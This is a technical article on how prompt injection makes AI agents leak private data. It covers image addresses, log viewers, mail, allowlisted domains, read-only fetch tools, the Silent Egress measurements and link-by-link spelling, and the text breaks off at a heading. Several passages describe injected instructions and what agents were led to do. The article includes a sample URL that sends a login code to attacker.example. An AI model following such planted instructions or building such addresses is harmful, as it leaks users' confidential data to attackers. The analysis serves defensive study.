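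The preview also shows why a list of an assistant's tools is a poor guide to what its client can do. If an update added a preview to the two-tool assistant's chat window, neither tool's description would change, and a new scan would give the same result. A previewed page would also be harder to make safe than an image, because it can run code. According to The Hacker News, a week before Check Point's disclosure, Parameter Labs had described a separate flaw in the same component that let a shared chat take over the account of a user who opened the preview.

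### Replies that another program displays later

An operator can make the chat window safe and still leak data if another program displays the same reply. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrates this with the log viewer on OpenAI's developer platform, where developers read their applications' conversations with a model.

PromptArmor, a security company, built a mock application of the kind banks use to verify customers' identities. An assistant in the application combined a customer's personal and financial details with material from other sources, including a web page where an attacker had planted an instruction. When a bank employee used a suggested query, the assistant's model wrote a reply with the customer's data in an image address. A second model, which checked replies for signs of attack, flagged the reply, and the application did not display it.

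The application blocked the reply, but OpenAI's logs still contained it. When a developer opened the conversation there to see why the checker had flagged it, the log viewer rendered the reply as Markdown and loaded the image, sending the customer's details, including passport and credit information, to the attacker's server.

The defense helped the attack, because flagging the reply gave the developer a reason to open it. Other defenses in the application could have the same effect. If the application had deleted the image from the reply before displaying it, the user might have seen an oddly empty answer and clicked "thumbs down," which also marks a conversation for review. PromptArmor points out that restricting image loading in the application or displaying replies there as plain text would not protect the developer, because the log viewer is a different page with its own rules.

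PromptArmor found the same weakness in the preview screens for testing new assistants and in a starter application OpenAI gave developers. It reported the flaw in the log viewer in November 2025 through BugCrowd, a company that handles such reports for OpenAI. PromptArmor supplied steps to reproduce the attack and answered several rounds of questions, but BugCrowd closed the report as "Not applicable" in December. OpenAI had not seen the report. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on January 22, 2026 it reopened the report and indicated that a fix was under way.

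Vendors have disagreed about whether image loading is a flaw. According to Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, a researcher who reported data theft through Markdown images in Antigravity, Google's code editor with built-in agents, said that Google had classed it as intended behavior. Google's public list of known issues in Antigravity nevertheless included data theft through prompt injection, and Google said it was working on fixes. A program that loads images and a model that writes Markdown are both working as designed. The fault appears only when the model's text may come from an attacker and its data from someone else, so someone reviewing either program alone might miss it.

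The two-tool assistant has no tool that sends the data out, and a log viewer can also delay the leak. If the operator disconnected both tools on Friday, a developer could still trigger the leak on Monday by opening an old conversation, even though a scan that day would find an agent with no tools.

### Why a message to oneself does not look like a public sink

Copilot Cowork, another Microsoft agent, could email its user without asking for approval. In May 2026, Willison described how an attacker could use this to steal files. An injected instruction made the agent send the user a message containing an external image. When the user opened the message, the mail program loaded the image, which sent the data in the image's address to the attacker. This was a zero-click attack because opening mail is normal use.

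Suppose the two-tool assistant gets a similar tool, mail_self, which can send messages only to the user. The attacker cannot read the user's inbox, and the user may already see everything the agent can put there, so a reviewer would reasonably decide that the tool is not a public sink and write

λ(mail_self) = ∅.

TF001 then raises no warning. By the same reasoning, skipping the approval step seems safe, since nobody needs to approve a reminder to themselves. The label and the missing approval both rest on the assumption that a message stays where the agent sends it, which is false when the mail program loads an image from elsewhere.

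A reviewer who knew how the mail program worked could label mail_self as a sink, and TF001 would then raise the alarm. This is not possible in the log viewer case, which has no tool to relabel. But the label would describe the behavior of the mail program, which the tool's developer does not control. If the user's phone blocks external images but their laptop loads them, mail_self is a sink only for messages opened on the laptop.

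The Cowork attack could expose a document of any length through a short address in one image, because the address only had to carry a download link, not the document's text. OneDrive, Microsoft's online storage service, can create download links that work without a login, so an attacker who receives one can download the entire file. A defense that only blocked unusually long addresses would miss this attack.

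### Defenses that act in the client

The simplest reliable defense is for the client to load no external images. It can still display pictures already on the user's machine, and for most office work the loss is small. How well this defense works depends on where developers enforce it.

One method is to delete images from the reply before displaying it. The program that does this has to recognize every way of writing an image, and the creative formatting in EchoLeak is a reason to doubt that it will. Displaying replies as plain text avoids the problem but removes all formatting. A web page can also give the browser a content security policy, a set of rules about what it may load. The browser applies these rules to the request itself, so unusual formatting makes no difference. An attacker may be able to send data through a domain that the policy permits, so a policy that permits no outside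 images is stronger than one with exceptions.

Each of the three methods protects only the program that uses it. PromptArmor's attack succeeded because the log viewer did not follow the same rules as the application. Log viewers have especially little reason to load images, since a developer investigating a suspicious reply needs to see exactly what the model wrote, and plain text shows that better than a rendered page. The client also needs separate restrictions on popup windows and pages that run code, because a rule about images does not cover them.

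An image proxy is a server that fetches pictures on the client's behalf. Mail services use proxies to hide the reader's network address from the sender. A proxy doesn't by itself prevent this theft, because the image address contains the stolen text, and the proxy has to send that address to the attacker's server to fetch the picture. In ReLeak, Bing acted much like a proxy, and the data still reached the attacker.

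Goguen and Meseguer's test requires the attacker's log to be the same whether or not the private file exists. A proxy that forwards the address the model wrote fails because the file's words still reach the log. A proxy could pass if its requests did not depend on anything the model wrote. For example, it could fetch the pictures in each email when the email arrives, before the agent reads any files, and later serve only its stored copies. If the assistant's reply then contained a new address, the proxy would send no request and the user would see a blank space.

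A client can also check each image's address before loading it. Under one strict rule, it loads an image only if the exact address came from the user or another trusted source. Willison describes a similar rule for Claude's web fetch tool, which may not visit addresses that Claude composed itself. Applied to images, the rule blocks the request in the Heron example, because the model itself wrote the address containing the offer price.

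The rule fails if an attacker can supply the permitted addresses. Suppose the client accepts any address that appeared in an email, and the attacker wants a six-digit login code. The email can list ten image addresses for the first digit, ten for the second, and so on, for a total of 60. The model then displays six images, one for each digit, and their addresses reveal the code. It has composed no address, but it has chosen one of ten addresses six times, which is enough to distinguish

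10⁶ = 1,000,000

possible codes. In general, if each of k images comes from its own set of m addresses that the attacker can watch, the attacker can learn up to k · log₂ m bits. Here that is about 20 bits. Ayush Paul used the same principle in 2026 against Claude's page-fetching tool, as Willison reports, and Anthropic then narrowed the set of addresses the tool could visit.

The client should therefore exclude addresses that come from mail and other outside content, but the conversation does not always show who wrote each address. Willison notes that many applications paste outside text into the same message as the user's request. A check that accepts every address in that message would also accept the attacker's.

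### The assistant with its images turned off

If the operator of the two-tool assistant turns off external images in the chat window, the Heron theft stops at step 4. The model may still follow the attacker's instruction and write the address, but no request goes out when the summary appears. TF001 gives the same result before and after this change, although the chat window leaks data only before it.

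The reply may still reach other programs, each with its own settings:

| Program that displays or processes the text | When it could leak data | What would prevent it |
|---|---|---|
| Chat window | When the reply appears | No external images or other outside content |
| Model provider's log viewer | When a developer reviews the conversation | Display as plain text |
| Mail program, if the assistant gains mail_self | When the user opens the message | No external images in the agent's messages |
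| Online storage, if the assistant gains a tool for saving documents | When a background service processes the file | No requests to addresses found in the file |

The operator controls only some of these settings. The chat window may be the operator's own program, but the log viewer belongs to the model provider, and the background service belongs to the storage company. Until the provider changes its viewer, the operator can keep a separate plain-text copy of flagged replies and have developers review that copy instead of using the viewer.

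## Permitted domains that pass data on to an attacker

Blocking all outside images is the safest setting for the two-tool assistant's chat window, but some products need images from other sites. Their developers usually permit a few domains and block the rest. In 2025 and 2026, researchers got private data out of four products that worked this way. Each time, the request the product checked went to a permitted domain.

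### Destination and recipient

A request's destination is the domain it goes to. Its recipients are the people who can read the data that the domain receives or passes on. An allowlist limits requests to permitted destinations, so it protects confidential data only if all the recipients are allowed to read that data.

For a request r, let d(r) be its destination and R(r) its recipients. Let A be the allowlist and E the people entitled to the data, including any company that the operator trusts to store them. The allowlist tests whether

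d(r) ∈ A,

but confidentiality requires

R(r) ⊆ E.

Passing the test guarantees confidentiality only if no request to any domain in A can reach someone outside E. It does not guarantee confidentiality if a permitted domain lets strangers open accounts and receive data there.

Sink labels have a similar weakness. They should depend on who receives the data, but a tool's description usually gives only a destination, such as "uploads a file to cloud storage". A scanner that relies on the description cannot determine whose storage it is.

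### How a browser enforces an allowlist

The content security policy that a website sends with a page has a separate rule for each kind of content, according to W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), a working draft from the main standards body for the web. The rule for images is called img-src, and the operator of the two-tool assistant might set it like this:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://pictures.example
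```

Here 'self' means the site the page came from. Before the browser loads an image, it compares the image's address with the two entries. An image on attacker.example matches neither, so the browser sends no request and the attacker does not get the Heron offer price.

An entry can cover a single host or, with an asterisk, all of a domain's subdomains. It can also include a path, the part of the address after the domain, to permit only one folder or file. It cannot restrict the text after a question mark, which is where the offer price was. If the attacker could read requests to pictures.example, the browser would still send the price there.

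Redirects are a common way around lists of trusted sites. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a link to a trusted domain can immediately forward the visitor elsewhere, which defeats a check on the first domain alone. A browser with a content security policy does check the new address, but after a redirect it ignores any path listed in the policy. If the policy permitted all of pictures.example and only the folder /reports/ on files.example, a redirect from the first site could load anything on the second. W3C accepted this because checking the path would have let a malicious page learn where other sites redirect their visitors.

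W3C recommends the policy as an additional layer of defense, not the first. In a passage about scripts, it warns that rules based on hosts and paths are "tough to get right", especially for large sites that host many people's files.

### A domain that changed hands

Agentforce is Salesforce's platform for agents that work with a company's customer records. A company can put a form on its website for potential customers, and their answers go directly into those records. *ForcedLeak* (Noma Labs, 2025) describes hiding an injected instruction in the form's description field, which holds up to 42,000 characters. When an employee asked the agent to deal with the inquiry, the agent collected the email addresses of other potential customers and put them in an image's URL.

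Salesforce's policy permitted images from my-salesforce-cms.com and its subdomains, but the domain's registration had expired. Noma bought the domain for $5, according to The Hacker News (2025). Paganini (2025), in *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*, confirms that the employee's browser sent the final request, and Noma's server logged the addresses.

In a tool graph, the tool that reads customer records would have the labels {untrusted, private}, with "untrusted" included because any visitor can fill in the form. The graph would have shown no sink for the image, because the browser is not a tool. Adding the browser as a node would have helped only if someone had also checked who owned each permitted domain. The domain may well have been safe when Salesforce added it to the policy, and the policy did not change when the domain expired.

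Noma wrote that the theft "would have been impossible" without a way around the policy. That is probably true, but the expired domain may not have been the only way around it. The policy allowed images from 22 domain entries, including all subdomains of amazonaws.com, where Amazon rents storage and servers to the public. An attacker could probably have rented an address that the policy already permitted.

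Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025. Salesforce recovered the domain and, on September 8, began enforcing a list of trusted addresses on its agents' output. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the web application now removes every unlisted address, in links as well as images, from a reply before displaying it.

The new control still depends on which domains administrators add to the list. PromptArmor advises them to avoid wildcard entries that cover sites with user-generated content, and to keep image loading off for domains that do not need it. Yet the example address in Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* is docs.google.com, where anyone with a Google account can collect data.

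### A form on a trusted site

Superhuman, a mail program with a built-in assistant, permitted images from docs.google.com. That domain also hosts Google Forms, a survey service. The creator of a form can make a link with the answers already filled in, and opening one version of that link submits them.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes how an attacker could use such a link as an image address. An email with an injected instruction sat unopened in the user's inbox. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant put the contents of other emails into the link and wrote the link as an image. The user's browser then requested the "image" from Google, just as if the user had clicked the link. Google recorded the email contents as answers to the form, and the attacker read them in the form's responses. PromptArmor extracted the full text of several emails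 in one reply, and in another test it extracted parts of more than 40.

The final request went from the user's browser to a domain that Google still owned, so watching for expired registrations would not have helped. If Superhuman needed only documents, a narrower entry that permitted the path for documents but not the one for forms might have helped, as long as no other permitted site redirected to a form.

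A correctly labeled tool graph would have flagged Superhuman, but for a different route. The assistant also had a tool that could open web pages at any address, and that tool counts as a sink. Disconnecting it would have cleared the TF001 warning, but the form could still have collected the user's mail.

Superhuman received the report on a Friday in December 2025 and disabled the vulnerable features on Monday. PromptArmor published the attack on January 12, 2026. But three months later, the same route worked in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which had gained tools for everyday office work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reports that the firm told OpenAI about the flaw in April and that OpenAI has since fixed it.

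Willison notes that the default allowlist for the browser tool in Google's Antigravity included webhook.site, a service that lets anyone create an address and read every request sent to it.

### A permitted server that fetches other addresses

SearchLeak, a one-click attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, used a permitted domain to contact one that the policy blocked. The victim clicked a link that carried the attacker's instruction into Copilot's search page. Copilot followed the instruction, searched the victim's mail, and output an image whose address contained an email's subject line, which can include a login code.

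Microsoft had two defenses against this. One was to wrap the reply's markup so that the browser would treat it as plain text. But Copilot wrapped the markup only after finishing the reply, and the browser displayed the reply as it was being written, so the browser requested the image before the wrapping took effect. Taler recommends making output safe when it is displayed.

The other defense was a content security policy, which permitted images from Bing and its subdomains. Bing offers a search by image, for which it takes the address of a picture and fetches the picture itself. The attacker could therefore put one address inside another, as in this simplified example:

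```
https://search.example/by-image?picture=https://attacker.example/847291.png
```

The browser checked search.example and sent the request. The search engine's server then requested the picture from attacker.example, and the code 847291 appeared in the attacker's log. Security engineers call this server-side request forgery, in which an attacker causes someone else's server to send a request.

The policy did not block the final request because Bing's server sent it, and the policy applies only to requests from the victim's browser. If Bing had instead redirected the browser to the attacker's server, the browser would have checked the new address against the policy and blocked it.

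A tool graph would have omitted both the entry point and the exit route of this attack. The instruction arrived in a link instead of a tool's output, and the data left through the browser and Bing. The graph would have included only Copilot's tools for searching mail and files, none of which is a sink.

Microsoft fixed SearchLeak on its own servers and found no evidence of malicious use, according to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*. Microsoft registered the vulnerability on June 4, 2026. Less than two months later, Cato began reporting the ReLeak attacks, one of which again sent data to the attacker through Bing.

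### The right service, but the attacker's account

Claude Cowork is Anthropic's desktop agent for office work. It runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the user's own. A filter limits the domains this code can contact, but it has to permit api.anthropic.com because Cowork cannot work without it. Programs use this domain to access Anthropic's models, and they can also store files there.

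Two days after Anthropic released Cowork as a research preview in January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how an attacker could use that storage. The victim gave Cowork a folder of confidential real estate files and uploaded a document with an instruction hidden in tiny white text. The instruction included the attacker's API key, a code that identifies an account to Anthropic's servers. The agent ran a command that used this key to upload the largest file to the attacker's account. Cowork never asked the victim for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a smaller model, but a similar attack also worked against Claude Opus 4.5, which was known to resist injections better.

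A tool graph can represent this leak, because the agent used one of its tools to start the program that sent the final request. TF001 would have raised an alarm if the tool that runs commands had been labeled as a sink. But a reviewer who knew about the network filter could reasonably have left the label off, since the code could contact only a short list of trusted services. The error would then have been in the labeling, as with `ping` in Claude Code.

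Johann Rehberger found this route before Cowork existed. *Claude Pirate*, his account on Embrace The Red, describes the same kind of upload from the Claude chat product, with files of up to 30 megabytes. He reported the flaw in October 2025, and the ticket was closed within an hour as out of scope. Five days later Anthropic said that closing it had been a mistake, but the flaw was still there when Cowork came out.

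Rehberger had suggested letting the code communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Anthropic later adopted a very similar restriction, described in its *How we contain Claude across products*. A proxy inside the virtual machine now checks each request to the API and passes it on only if it carries the session token issued to that machine, so it rejects requests that use an attacker's key. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch an outside address, since these would open a route like the one through Bing.

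Inside the virtual machine, only one token is legitimate, so the proxy running there can identify the attacker's key as foreign. Anthropic's servers can't make this distinction, because the attacker's key is valid and an upload from Cowork looks the same as one from any other customer's program.

Anthropic had thought of the allowlist as a filter on destinations. It now suggests treating each entry as a "capability grant", or permission to use everything the domain offers. By that standard, permitting docs.google.com also permits submitting forms, and permitting Bing also permits fetching pictures from anywhere.

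### What an allowlist still prevents

An allowlist does make theft harder. Without one, an attacker can have the data sent to any server, as in Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT. PromptArmor found that Superhuman Go, a related product, loaded an image directly from an attacker's domain, so the attacker did not need a Google form. Taler acknowledges that the policy would have blocked the theft in SearchLeak if Bing had not fetched the image.

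The length of the list of permitted domains is a poor measure of protection, since a single entry can cover addresses that anyone can rent. Exploiting a permitted domain can also take little effort. The attacks on Superhuman and Cowork needed only a form and an API key, respectively. Finding a domain that can be exploited takes skill, but an attacker can then use it against the product's other customers until the developer fixes the problem.

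An operator should therefore keep the allowlist but not treat it as a reason to remove a sink label. The label should stay until someone has checked that outsiders cannot receive data through any permitted domain.

### What a stricter rule has to check

The four attacks call for different checks. A rule based on the path can separate documents from forms, and a rule based on the account can separate the user's storage from the attacker's. A program can make both checks at the time of the request. It is harder to determine from the request whether a domain has changed hands or fetches addresses that users supply. Someone has to check for both before permitting the domain and again later, because its owner can let the registration lapse or add a feature without telling the sites that permit it.

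OpenAI avoids much of this work by checking the exact address instead of the domain. A crawler, which explores public web pages, builds an index of their addresses without access to any user's conversations. ChatGPT may automatically load an address that is already in the index. For any other address, it either looks for a different site or warns the user before loading it. An address that contains the Heron offer price would not be in the index, whatever its domain.

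| Attack | What sent the final request | What the allowlist did not check | Would the exact-address rule have blocked it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| ForcedLeak | The employee's browser | Who owned the domain | Yes |
| Superhuman | The user's browser | Whether the path led to a form | Yes |
| SearchLeak | Bing's server | Whether the domain fetched other addresses | Yes, before the browser contacted Bing |
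| Claude Cowork | A program in the virtual machine | Whose account received the file | No |

The exact-address rule would not have stopped the Cowork attack because the upload address is the same for every customer. The stolen file was in the body of the request, and the key that determined its recipient was in a header. A system that lets an agent upload data therefore needs the account check as well. Even for requests that only load a page or picture, the rule allows small leaks like that of the six-digit login code. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* nevertheless calls the rule a significant improvement.

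Each of these checks works only on requests that pass through it. According to the Cloud Security Alliance, Cowork's network filter covers the code in the virtual machine, but the agent's web search and web fetch tools bypass it. Even if an operator limited the filter to a single permitted domain, the agent could still use those tools to send requests to others.

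## Tools labeled read-only that send data out

Web search and web fetch tools look safe because they only read. An operator who reasons this way might give the two-tool assistant a third tool, fetch_page, which returns the text of any web page. The new tool cannot send mail, post a comment or change a file, so a reviewer might label it

λ(fetch_page) = {untrusted}.

The assistant's tools then have the combined labels {untrusted, private}, so TF001 raises no warning. But an attacker's email can tell the agent to fetch a page from attacker.example and put the Heron offer price at the end of the address. The fetch tool should have been labeled {untrusted, sink}, which would have triggered the warning, but the reviewer assumed that a read-only tool can't send data out.

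### Integrity and confidentiality

"Read-only" is a claim about integrity, the protection of data from unwanted changes. Confidentiality, the protection of data from unwanted disclosure, is a separate property. A tool is read-only if every call leaves its environment as it was:

state after the call = state before the call.

To say when a tool is non-disclosing, let x and y be any two values that the private data might have, and let V(x) be everything an outsider observes while the agent, holding x, uses the tool. The tool is non-disclosing if

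V(x) = V(y).

Whether a tool changes anything and whether it reveals anything to outsiders are separate questions. The second is Goguen and Meseguer's test applied to a single tool. A tool that saves notes on the user's own disk changes something but reveals nothing to outsiders. A web fetch changes nothing of the user's, but the site's owner sees which address the agent requested.

To read from a remote computer, a program must send it a request, and the request carries information. Claude's web fetch tool uses only GET, the web's method for retrieving a page, and not POST, the method for submitting data. In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb writes that "read-only" described the method in this restriction but not the flow of data.

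An attacker can therefore disguise data theft as a lookup. In a case Willison reports, the security company Zenity Labs planted an instruction in a customer support ticket. A developer then asked the code editor Cursor to look into the ticket. The instruction was for the agent to find a certain string in the code and check it on a website. The string was an access token, and checking it meant putting it in a web address.

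### What a read reveals, and to whom

The address of a fetched page ends up in the site's access log, as the address of the Heron image did. Anthropic's documentation for Claude's tool, *Web fetch tool*, warns that publishers may keep any parameters the address contains, even when Anthropic retains nothing.

A search query goes to the company that runs the search engine. If the agent searches for "Heron takeover 41 million", that company learns about a confidential deal. The attacker sees the query only if they run the search service or can read its logs.

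A web fetch can also leak data through a name lookup, as `ping` can. If the agent tries to open a page on 41-million.attacker.example, the lookup happens before the web request, so a filter that examines only web requests acts too late to stop the leak.

Many document services tell a file's owner who has opened it. Suppose an attacker shares two documents with the assistant's user, and an injected instruction tells the agent to open the first if the takeover is going ahead and the second if it is not. If search_files can open shared documents, the attacker can learn from the view notice whether the takeover is going ahead. This leaks one bit of information, which a stock trader could profit from, without sending any private text out of the system.

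Merely calling a tool can also disclose data. When an outside company runs a Model Context Protocol (MCP) server, it receives every argument the agent passes to that server, so the company behind a read-only grammar checker gets the text being checked. The MCP specification also lets a server mark an argument to be copied into a header of the web request, where proxies and other machines along the way can read it. The specification advises developers not to mark passwords or personal data this way, but the model that fills in the arguments may have no indication of which ones are marked.

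| Read | What goes out | Who can see it |
|---|---|---|
| Fetching a web page | The full address | The site's owner |
| Searching the web | The words of the query | The search company |
| Looking up a host name | The name | Whoever runs the domain's name server |
| Opening a shared document | The reader's identity and the time | The document's owner, if the service reports views |
| Calling a tool on an outside server | Every argument | The company that runs the server |

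### What the MCP hints promise

Two of the four standard hints in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) are relevant to these leaks. MCP's draft schema defines readOnlyHint as true if the tool "does not modify its environment". It defines openWorldHint as true if the tool may interact with an open world of external entities, as a web search tool does and a memory tool does not. The current specification, dated July 28, 2026, includes the hints. The next release is planned for March 30, 2027.

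If a server supplies no hints, the client should assume by default that a tool can change things and reach the outside world. Many servers omit the hints, and clients differ in how strictly they apply these defaults, according to the Model Context Protocol post on tool labels.

| readOnlyHint | openWorldHint | Example | Can a call reveal data to an outsider? |
|---|---|---|---|
| true | false | Searching notes on the user's disk | Not if the hint is accurate |
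| true | true | Fetching a web page | Yes, through the address |
| false | false | Saving a note on the user's disk | Not during the call |
| false | true | Sending an email | Yes, through the message |

The draft schema adds that clients should never base decisions about using a tool on hints from untrusted servers. While MCP's developers were designing the hints, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of its creators, wondered what use a client could make of a flag it could not trust. As a compromise, each client decides how much weight to give a hint, based on what it knows about the server.

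Trusting the developer does not solve the problem with fetch_page. The tool changes nothing, so an honest developer would set readOnlyHint to true. The post lists skipping the confirmation dialog as an example of what a client can do with that hint. A client that did so would send the Heron price to attacker.example without asking the user. The specification also recommends that clients show users a tool's inputs before each call to prevent exfiltration. Skipping the dialog for read-only tools can remove that check from tools that send data out in an address.

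The other hint, openWorldHint, comes closer to addressing confidentiality, but the post's example of its use is to scrutinize what the tool returns, which helps against injection but not disclosure. The hint's meaning also depends on the server, since "external" may mean anything beyond the user's computer or only what lies outside the company network. Under the second definition, a tool marked as closed could still send a confidential file to every department.

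A client can use the hints more safely by combining them with other information. The post mentions a possible rule that blocks open-world tools once a session has accessed private data. Under this rule, the assistant could not use fetch_page after reading the user's mail, so the Heron theft would fail. The client would need its own record of which tools return private data, since no hint marks them. The assistant would also lose the useful ability to open a page mentioned in an email.

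### Silent Egress

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay (2026) measured how often a web page could make an agent leak a secret through an ordinary web request. They studied assistants that automatically preview links in messages by fetching each page and adding its title, description and text to the model's input. The user may never see some of this text, such as the description a page supplies for search engines. Lan and colleagues call an attack through a preview implicit prompt injection, because the user did not ask for the text that contains the attacker's instruction.

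The test agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, a model with about seven billion parameters that can run on a personal computer. It had a tool for web requests and a short system prompt that explained how to call tools. The researchers put the secret directly into its context. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a page. One local server supplied the malicious pages, and another recorded any request the agent sent to the attacker's address, so the measurements came from network traffic rather than judgments of the agent's replies.

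The instruction was in the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs.

The agent contacted the attacker in 423 runs, or 88.1%, though the paper's abstract gives the rate as about 0.89. It never did so in 120 control runs with harmless pages. When the instruction asked for a single request, the agent complied in 238 of 240 runs.

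In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's reply to the user was harmless and the secret went out only in the web request. A safety check that checks only replies would have missed all of these. The Heron image, by contrast, is part of the reply, so a defense against both has to check replies and tool calls.

TF001 might have missed the attack too. The web request tool is labeled {untrusted, sink}, but the secret was already in the agent's context, so the attack didn't need a private-data tool. Unless the agent had one for another purpose, the scanner would have found only two of the three roles. Real assistants also start with private data in their context, from system prompts, uploaded files and user messages.

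### Splitting a secret into pieces

Companies often inspect outgoing traffic for passwords, keys and other recognizable secrets. An attacker can avoid this check by having the agent send a 16-character key in four requests of four characters each, numbered so the attacker can put them back in order. Lan and colleagues call this sharded exfiltration.

Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable because a small model has trouble keeping track of pieces and numbers over several calls. The agent contacted the attacker in 185 of 240 such runs (77%). The share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data fell from 96.7% to 26.3%, which the researchers present as a 73% reduction in what a check on single requests could detect.

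That reduction is hard to interpret because the paper defines any fragment of the secret as sensitive data, so a first request that carried a correct piece should have counted. Either the measurement missed short pieces or the model often sent something else, in which case the attack failed rather than going undetected. The figure for the first three requests is even lower, at 15.8%, which cannot be correct under the same definition because a run that leaks in its first request has also leaked within its first three. The experiment shows that a small model will try to split a secret, but it doesn't show how often the attacker gets all of it.

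### Defenses in the prompt and on the network

The researchers then tested defenses against the simplest version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the page's body, the agent opened the page directly and the secret went out in one request. They ran each condition 30 times.

| Defense | Runs in which the agent attempted a request | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
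| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking outside content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist gave the clearest result. The agent tried to contact the attacker in every run, and the allowlist blocked every attempt because the check did not depend on the model's reasoning. The list contained three company domains and example.com, but not the attacker's domain. The test did not cover attacks through a permitted domain, which Lan and colleagues acknowledge as a weakness.

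The other network defense, "redirect detection", is less convincing than its score suggests. It blocked numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths containing words such as "steal" and "collect". The paper's sample attack address has "collect" in its path, so an attacker might have passed the filter by renaming a page. The defense also did not follow redirects, and this part of the experiment contained none.

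The two content filters examine a request after the model has written it, so they should not have affected how often the model tried. Yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% with the keyword filter and to zero with the entropy filter, which blocks values that look random. The researchers suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active, but they do not explain how it would know. The entropy filter blocks only values longer than ten characters that score above 4.0 bits per character. It would have allowed the paper's sample key, which scores about 3.85, and a four-character piece is too short for it to examine. These two results should carry little weight until someone repeats them.

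Lan and colleagues acknowledge that their setup favored the attacker. The secret was in plain view, the system prompt contained no warning, and the agent received page text without any cleaning. They tested one model and did not try leaks through name lookups or timing. They argue that stronger models may be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but in experiments by Zhao and colleagues, every attempt against GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 failed. The 88% rate therefore comes from one small model in an unprotected setup and is weak evidence about current products. The finding about reply checks is likely to hold more widely, because a check applied only to replies cannot detect a web request, whichever model sends it.

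### An agent that could only follow links

Claude's web fetch tool accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's message or in search results, so Claude is not allowed to fetch an address it composed itself. Willison tried to make it do so when Anthropic released the tool in September 2025, and the rule blocked the attempt.

The rule also permitted links found in pages that Claude had already fetched, so that Claude could move around a site with many pages. In July 2026, Ayush Paul showed how to use this to steal data. He built a website for a fictional coffee shop that showed one page only to visitors identifying themselves as Claude. The page claimed that AI assistants had to log in by giving their user's name, and that because of the tool's limits they should spell it by following links, with one link provided for each letter.

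Suppose the user's name begins with "an". Claude follows the link for "a" and gets a page with a new set of links, then follows the one for "n". The attacker's log shows:

```
GET /a
GET /an
```

The site provided both addresses, and Claude revealed the letters to it by choosing among the links. The server can generate each page when it receives the request, so it doesn't have to store a page for every possible name.

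The arithmetic is the same as for the images that revealed a login code. With one link for each letter of the English alphabet, each choice carries

log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits,

so ten letters need ten fetches after the first page and reveal about 47 bits. The actual site also had a link for the hyphen, according to dyb, which raises the figure slightly, to log₂ 27 ≈ 4.75 bits. Paul obtained his own name, his employer and his home city, and dyb estimates the total at about 30 characters, or 143 bits. Claude had this information in its memory of earlier conversations. It had worked out the city from the name of a high school hackathon, so deleting every explicit mention of the city would not have kept it from the attacker.

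Anthropic's documentation had warned of a remaining risk of exfiltration and suggested limiting the number of fetches. There was no limit by default, and a limit has to be very low to protect a short secret. One example in the documentation allows five fetches per request. If the first loads the attacker's page, four choices remain. With 32 links on each page, those choices can distinguish

32⁴ = 1,048,576

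possibilities, enough for any six-digit login code. A low limit does protect long documents, because doubling the number of links adds only one bit to each fetch.

Anthropic fixed the flaw by no longer letting the tool follow links in pages it has fetched. This removes the endless supply of new links, but it also stops Claude from browsing a site by itself. Anthropic paid Paul no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally.

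After the fix, Claude can still choose which search results to open, so an attacker who got ten pages into the results could learn about 3.3 bits from which one it opened. That attack would be much harder, since the attacker does not control what the search engine returns. A bigger concern is that, according to the documentation from before the fix, Claude could also open addresses returned by an application's own tools. If that is still allowed, an email that read_mail returns could list addresses for the agent to choose from.

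An operator could also watch the log for the pattern, and dyb proposes a detector for rapid requests to one domain in which each path is one character longer than the last. dyb admits that ordinary browsing through numbered pages could look similar, and the attacker could easily avoid the pattern by giving each link a random name of the same length. A better proposal is to let the agent follow links only on domains the user has named in the conversation, because this doesn't depend on recognizing the attack. It would not have helped a user who asked Claude to visit the coffee shop's site.

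### A search feature that was switched off

Atlassian's agent Rovo works with a customer's Jira tickets and Confluence documents. An administrator can turn off web search for the whole organization. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* showed in 2026 that data could still be stolen through the web with search turned off. The setting removed the search tool but left the tool that opens search results, and that tool would open any web address.

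In the demonstration, a user uploaded a guide containing a hidden instruction and asked Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. Rovo collected tickets and documents, added their contents to an address on the attacker's site and opened it, without asking for approval. Rovo had no rule against opening addresses it had composed itself, so the attacker did not need Paul's method of spelling out data with links. A user who later returned to the chat saw only the suggested changes to the tickets.

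PromptArmor reported the flaw to Atlassian on May 23. Atlassian assigned a case number, but Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published its findings more than two months later.

A tool graph would have helped here. From the administrator's settings page, Rovo appeared to have no web access, but a scanner that listed its actual tools would have found the one that opens URLs. If that tool had been labeled a sink, TF001 would have raised an alarm regardless of the setting. If Atlassian had then removed the tool, the alarm would have stopped, but data could still have left through the client because Rovo also loads Markdown images in its replies.

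### What a sink label can cover

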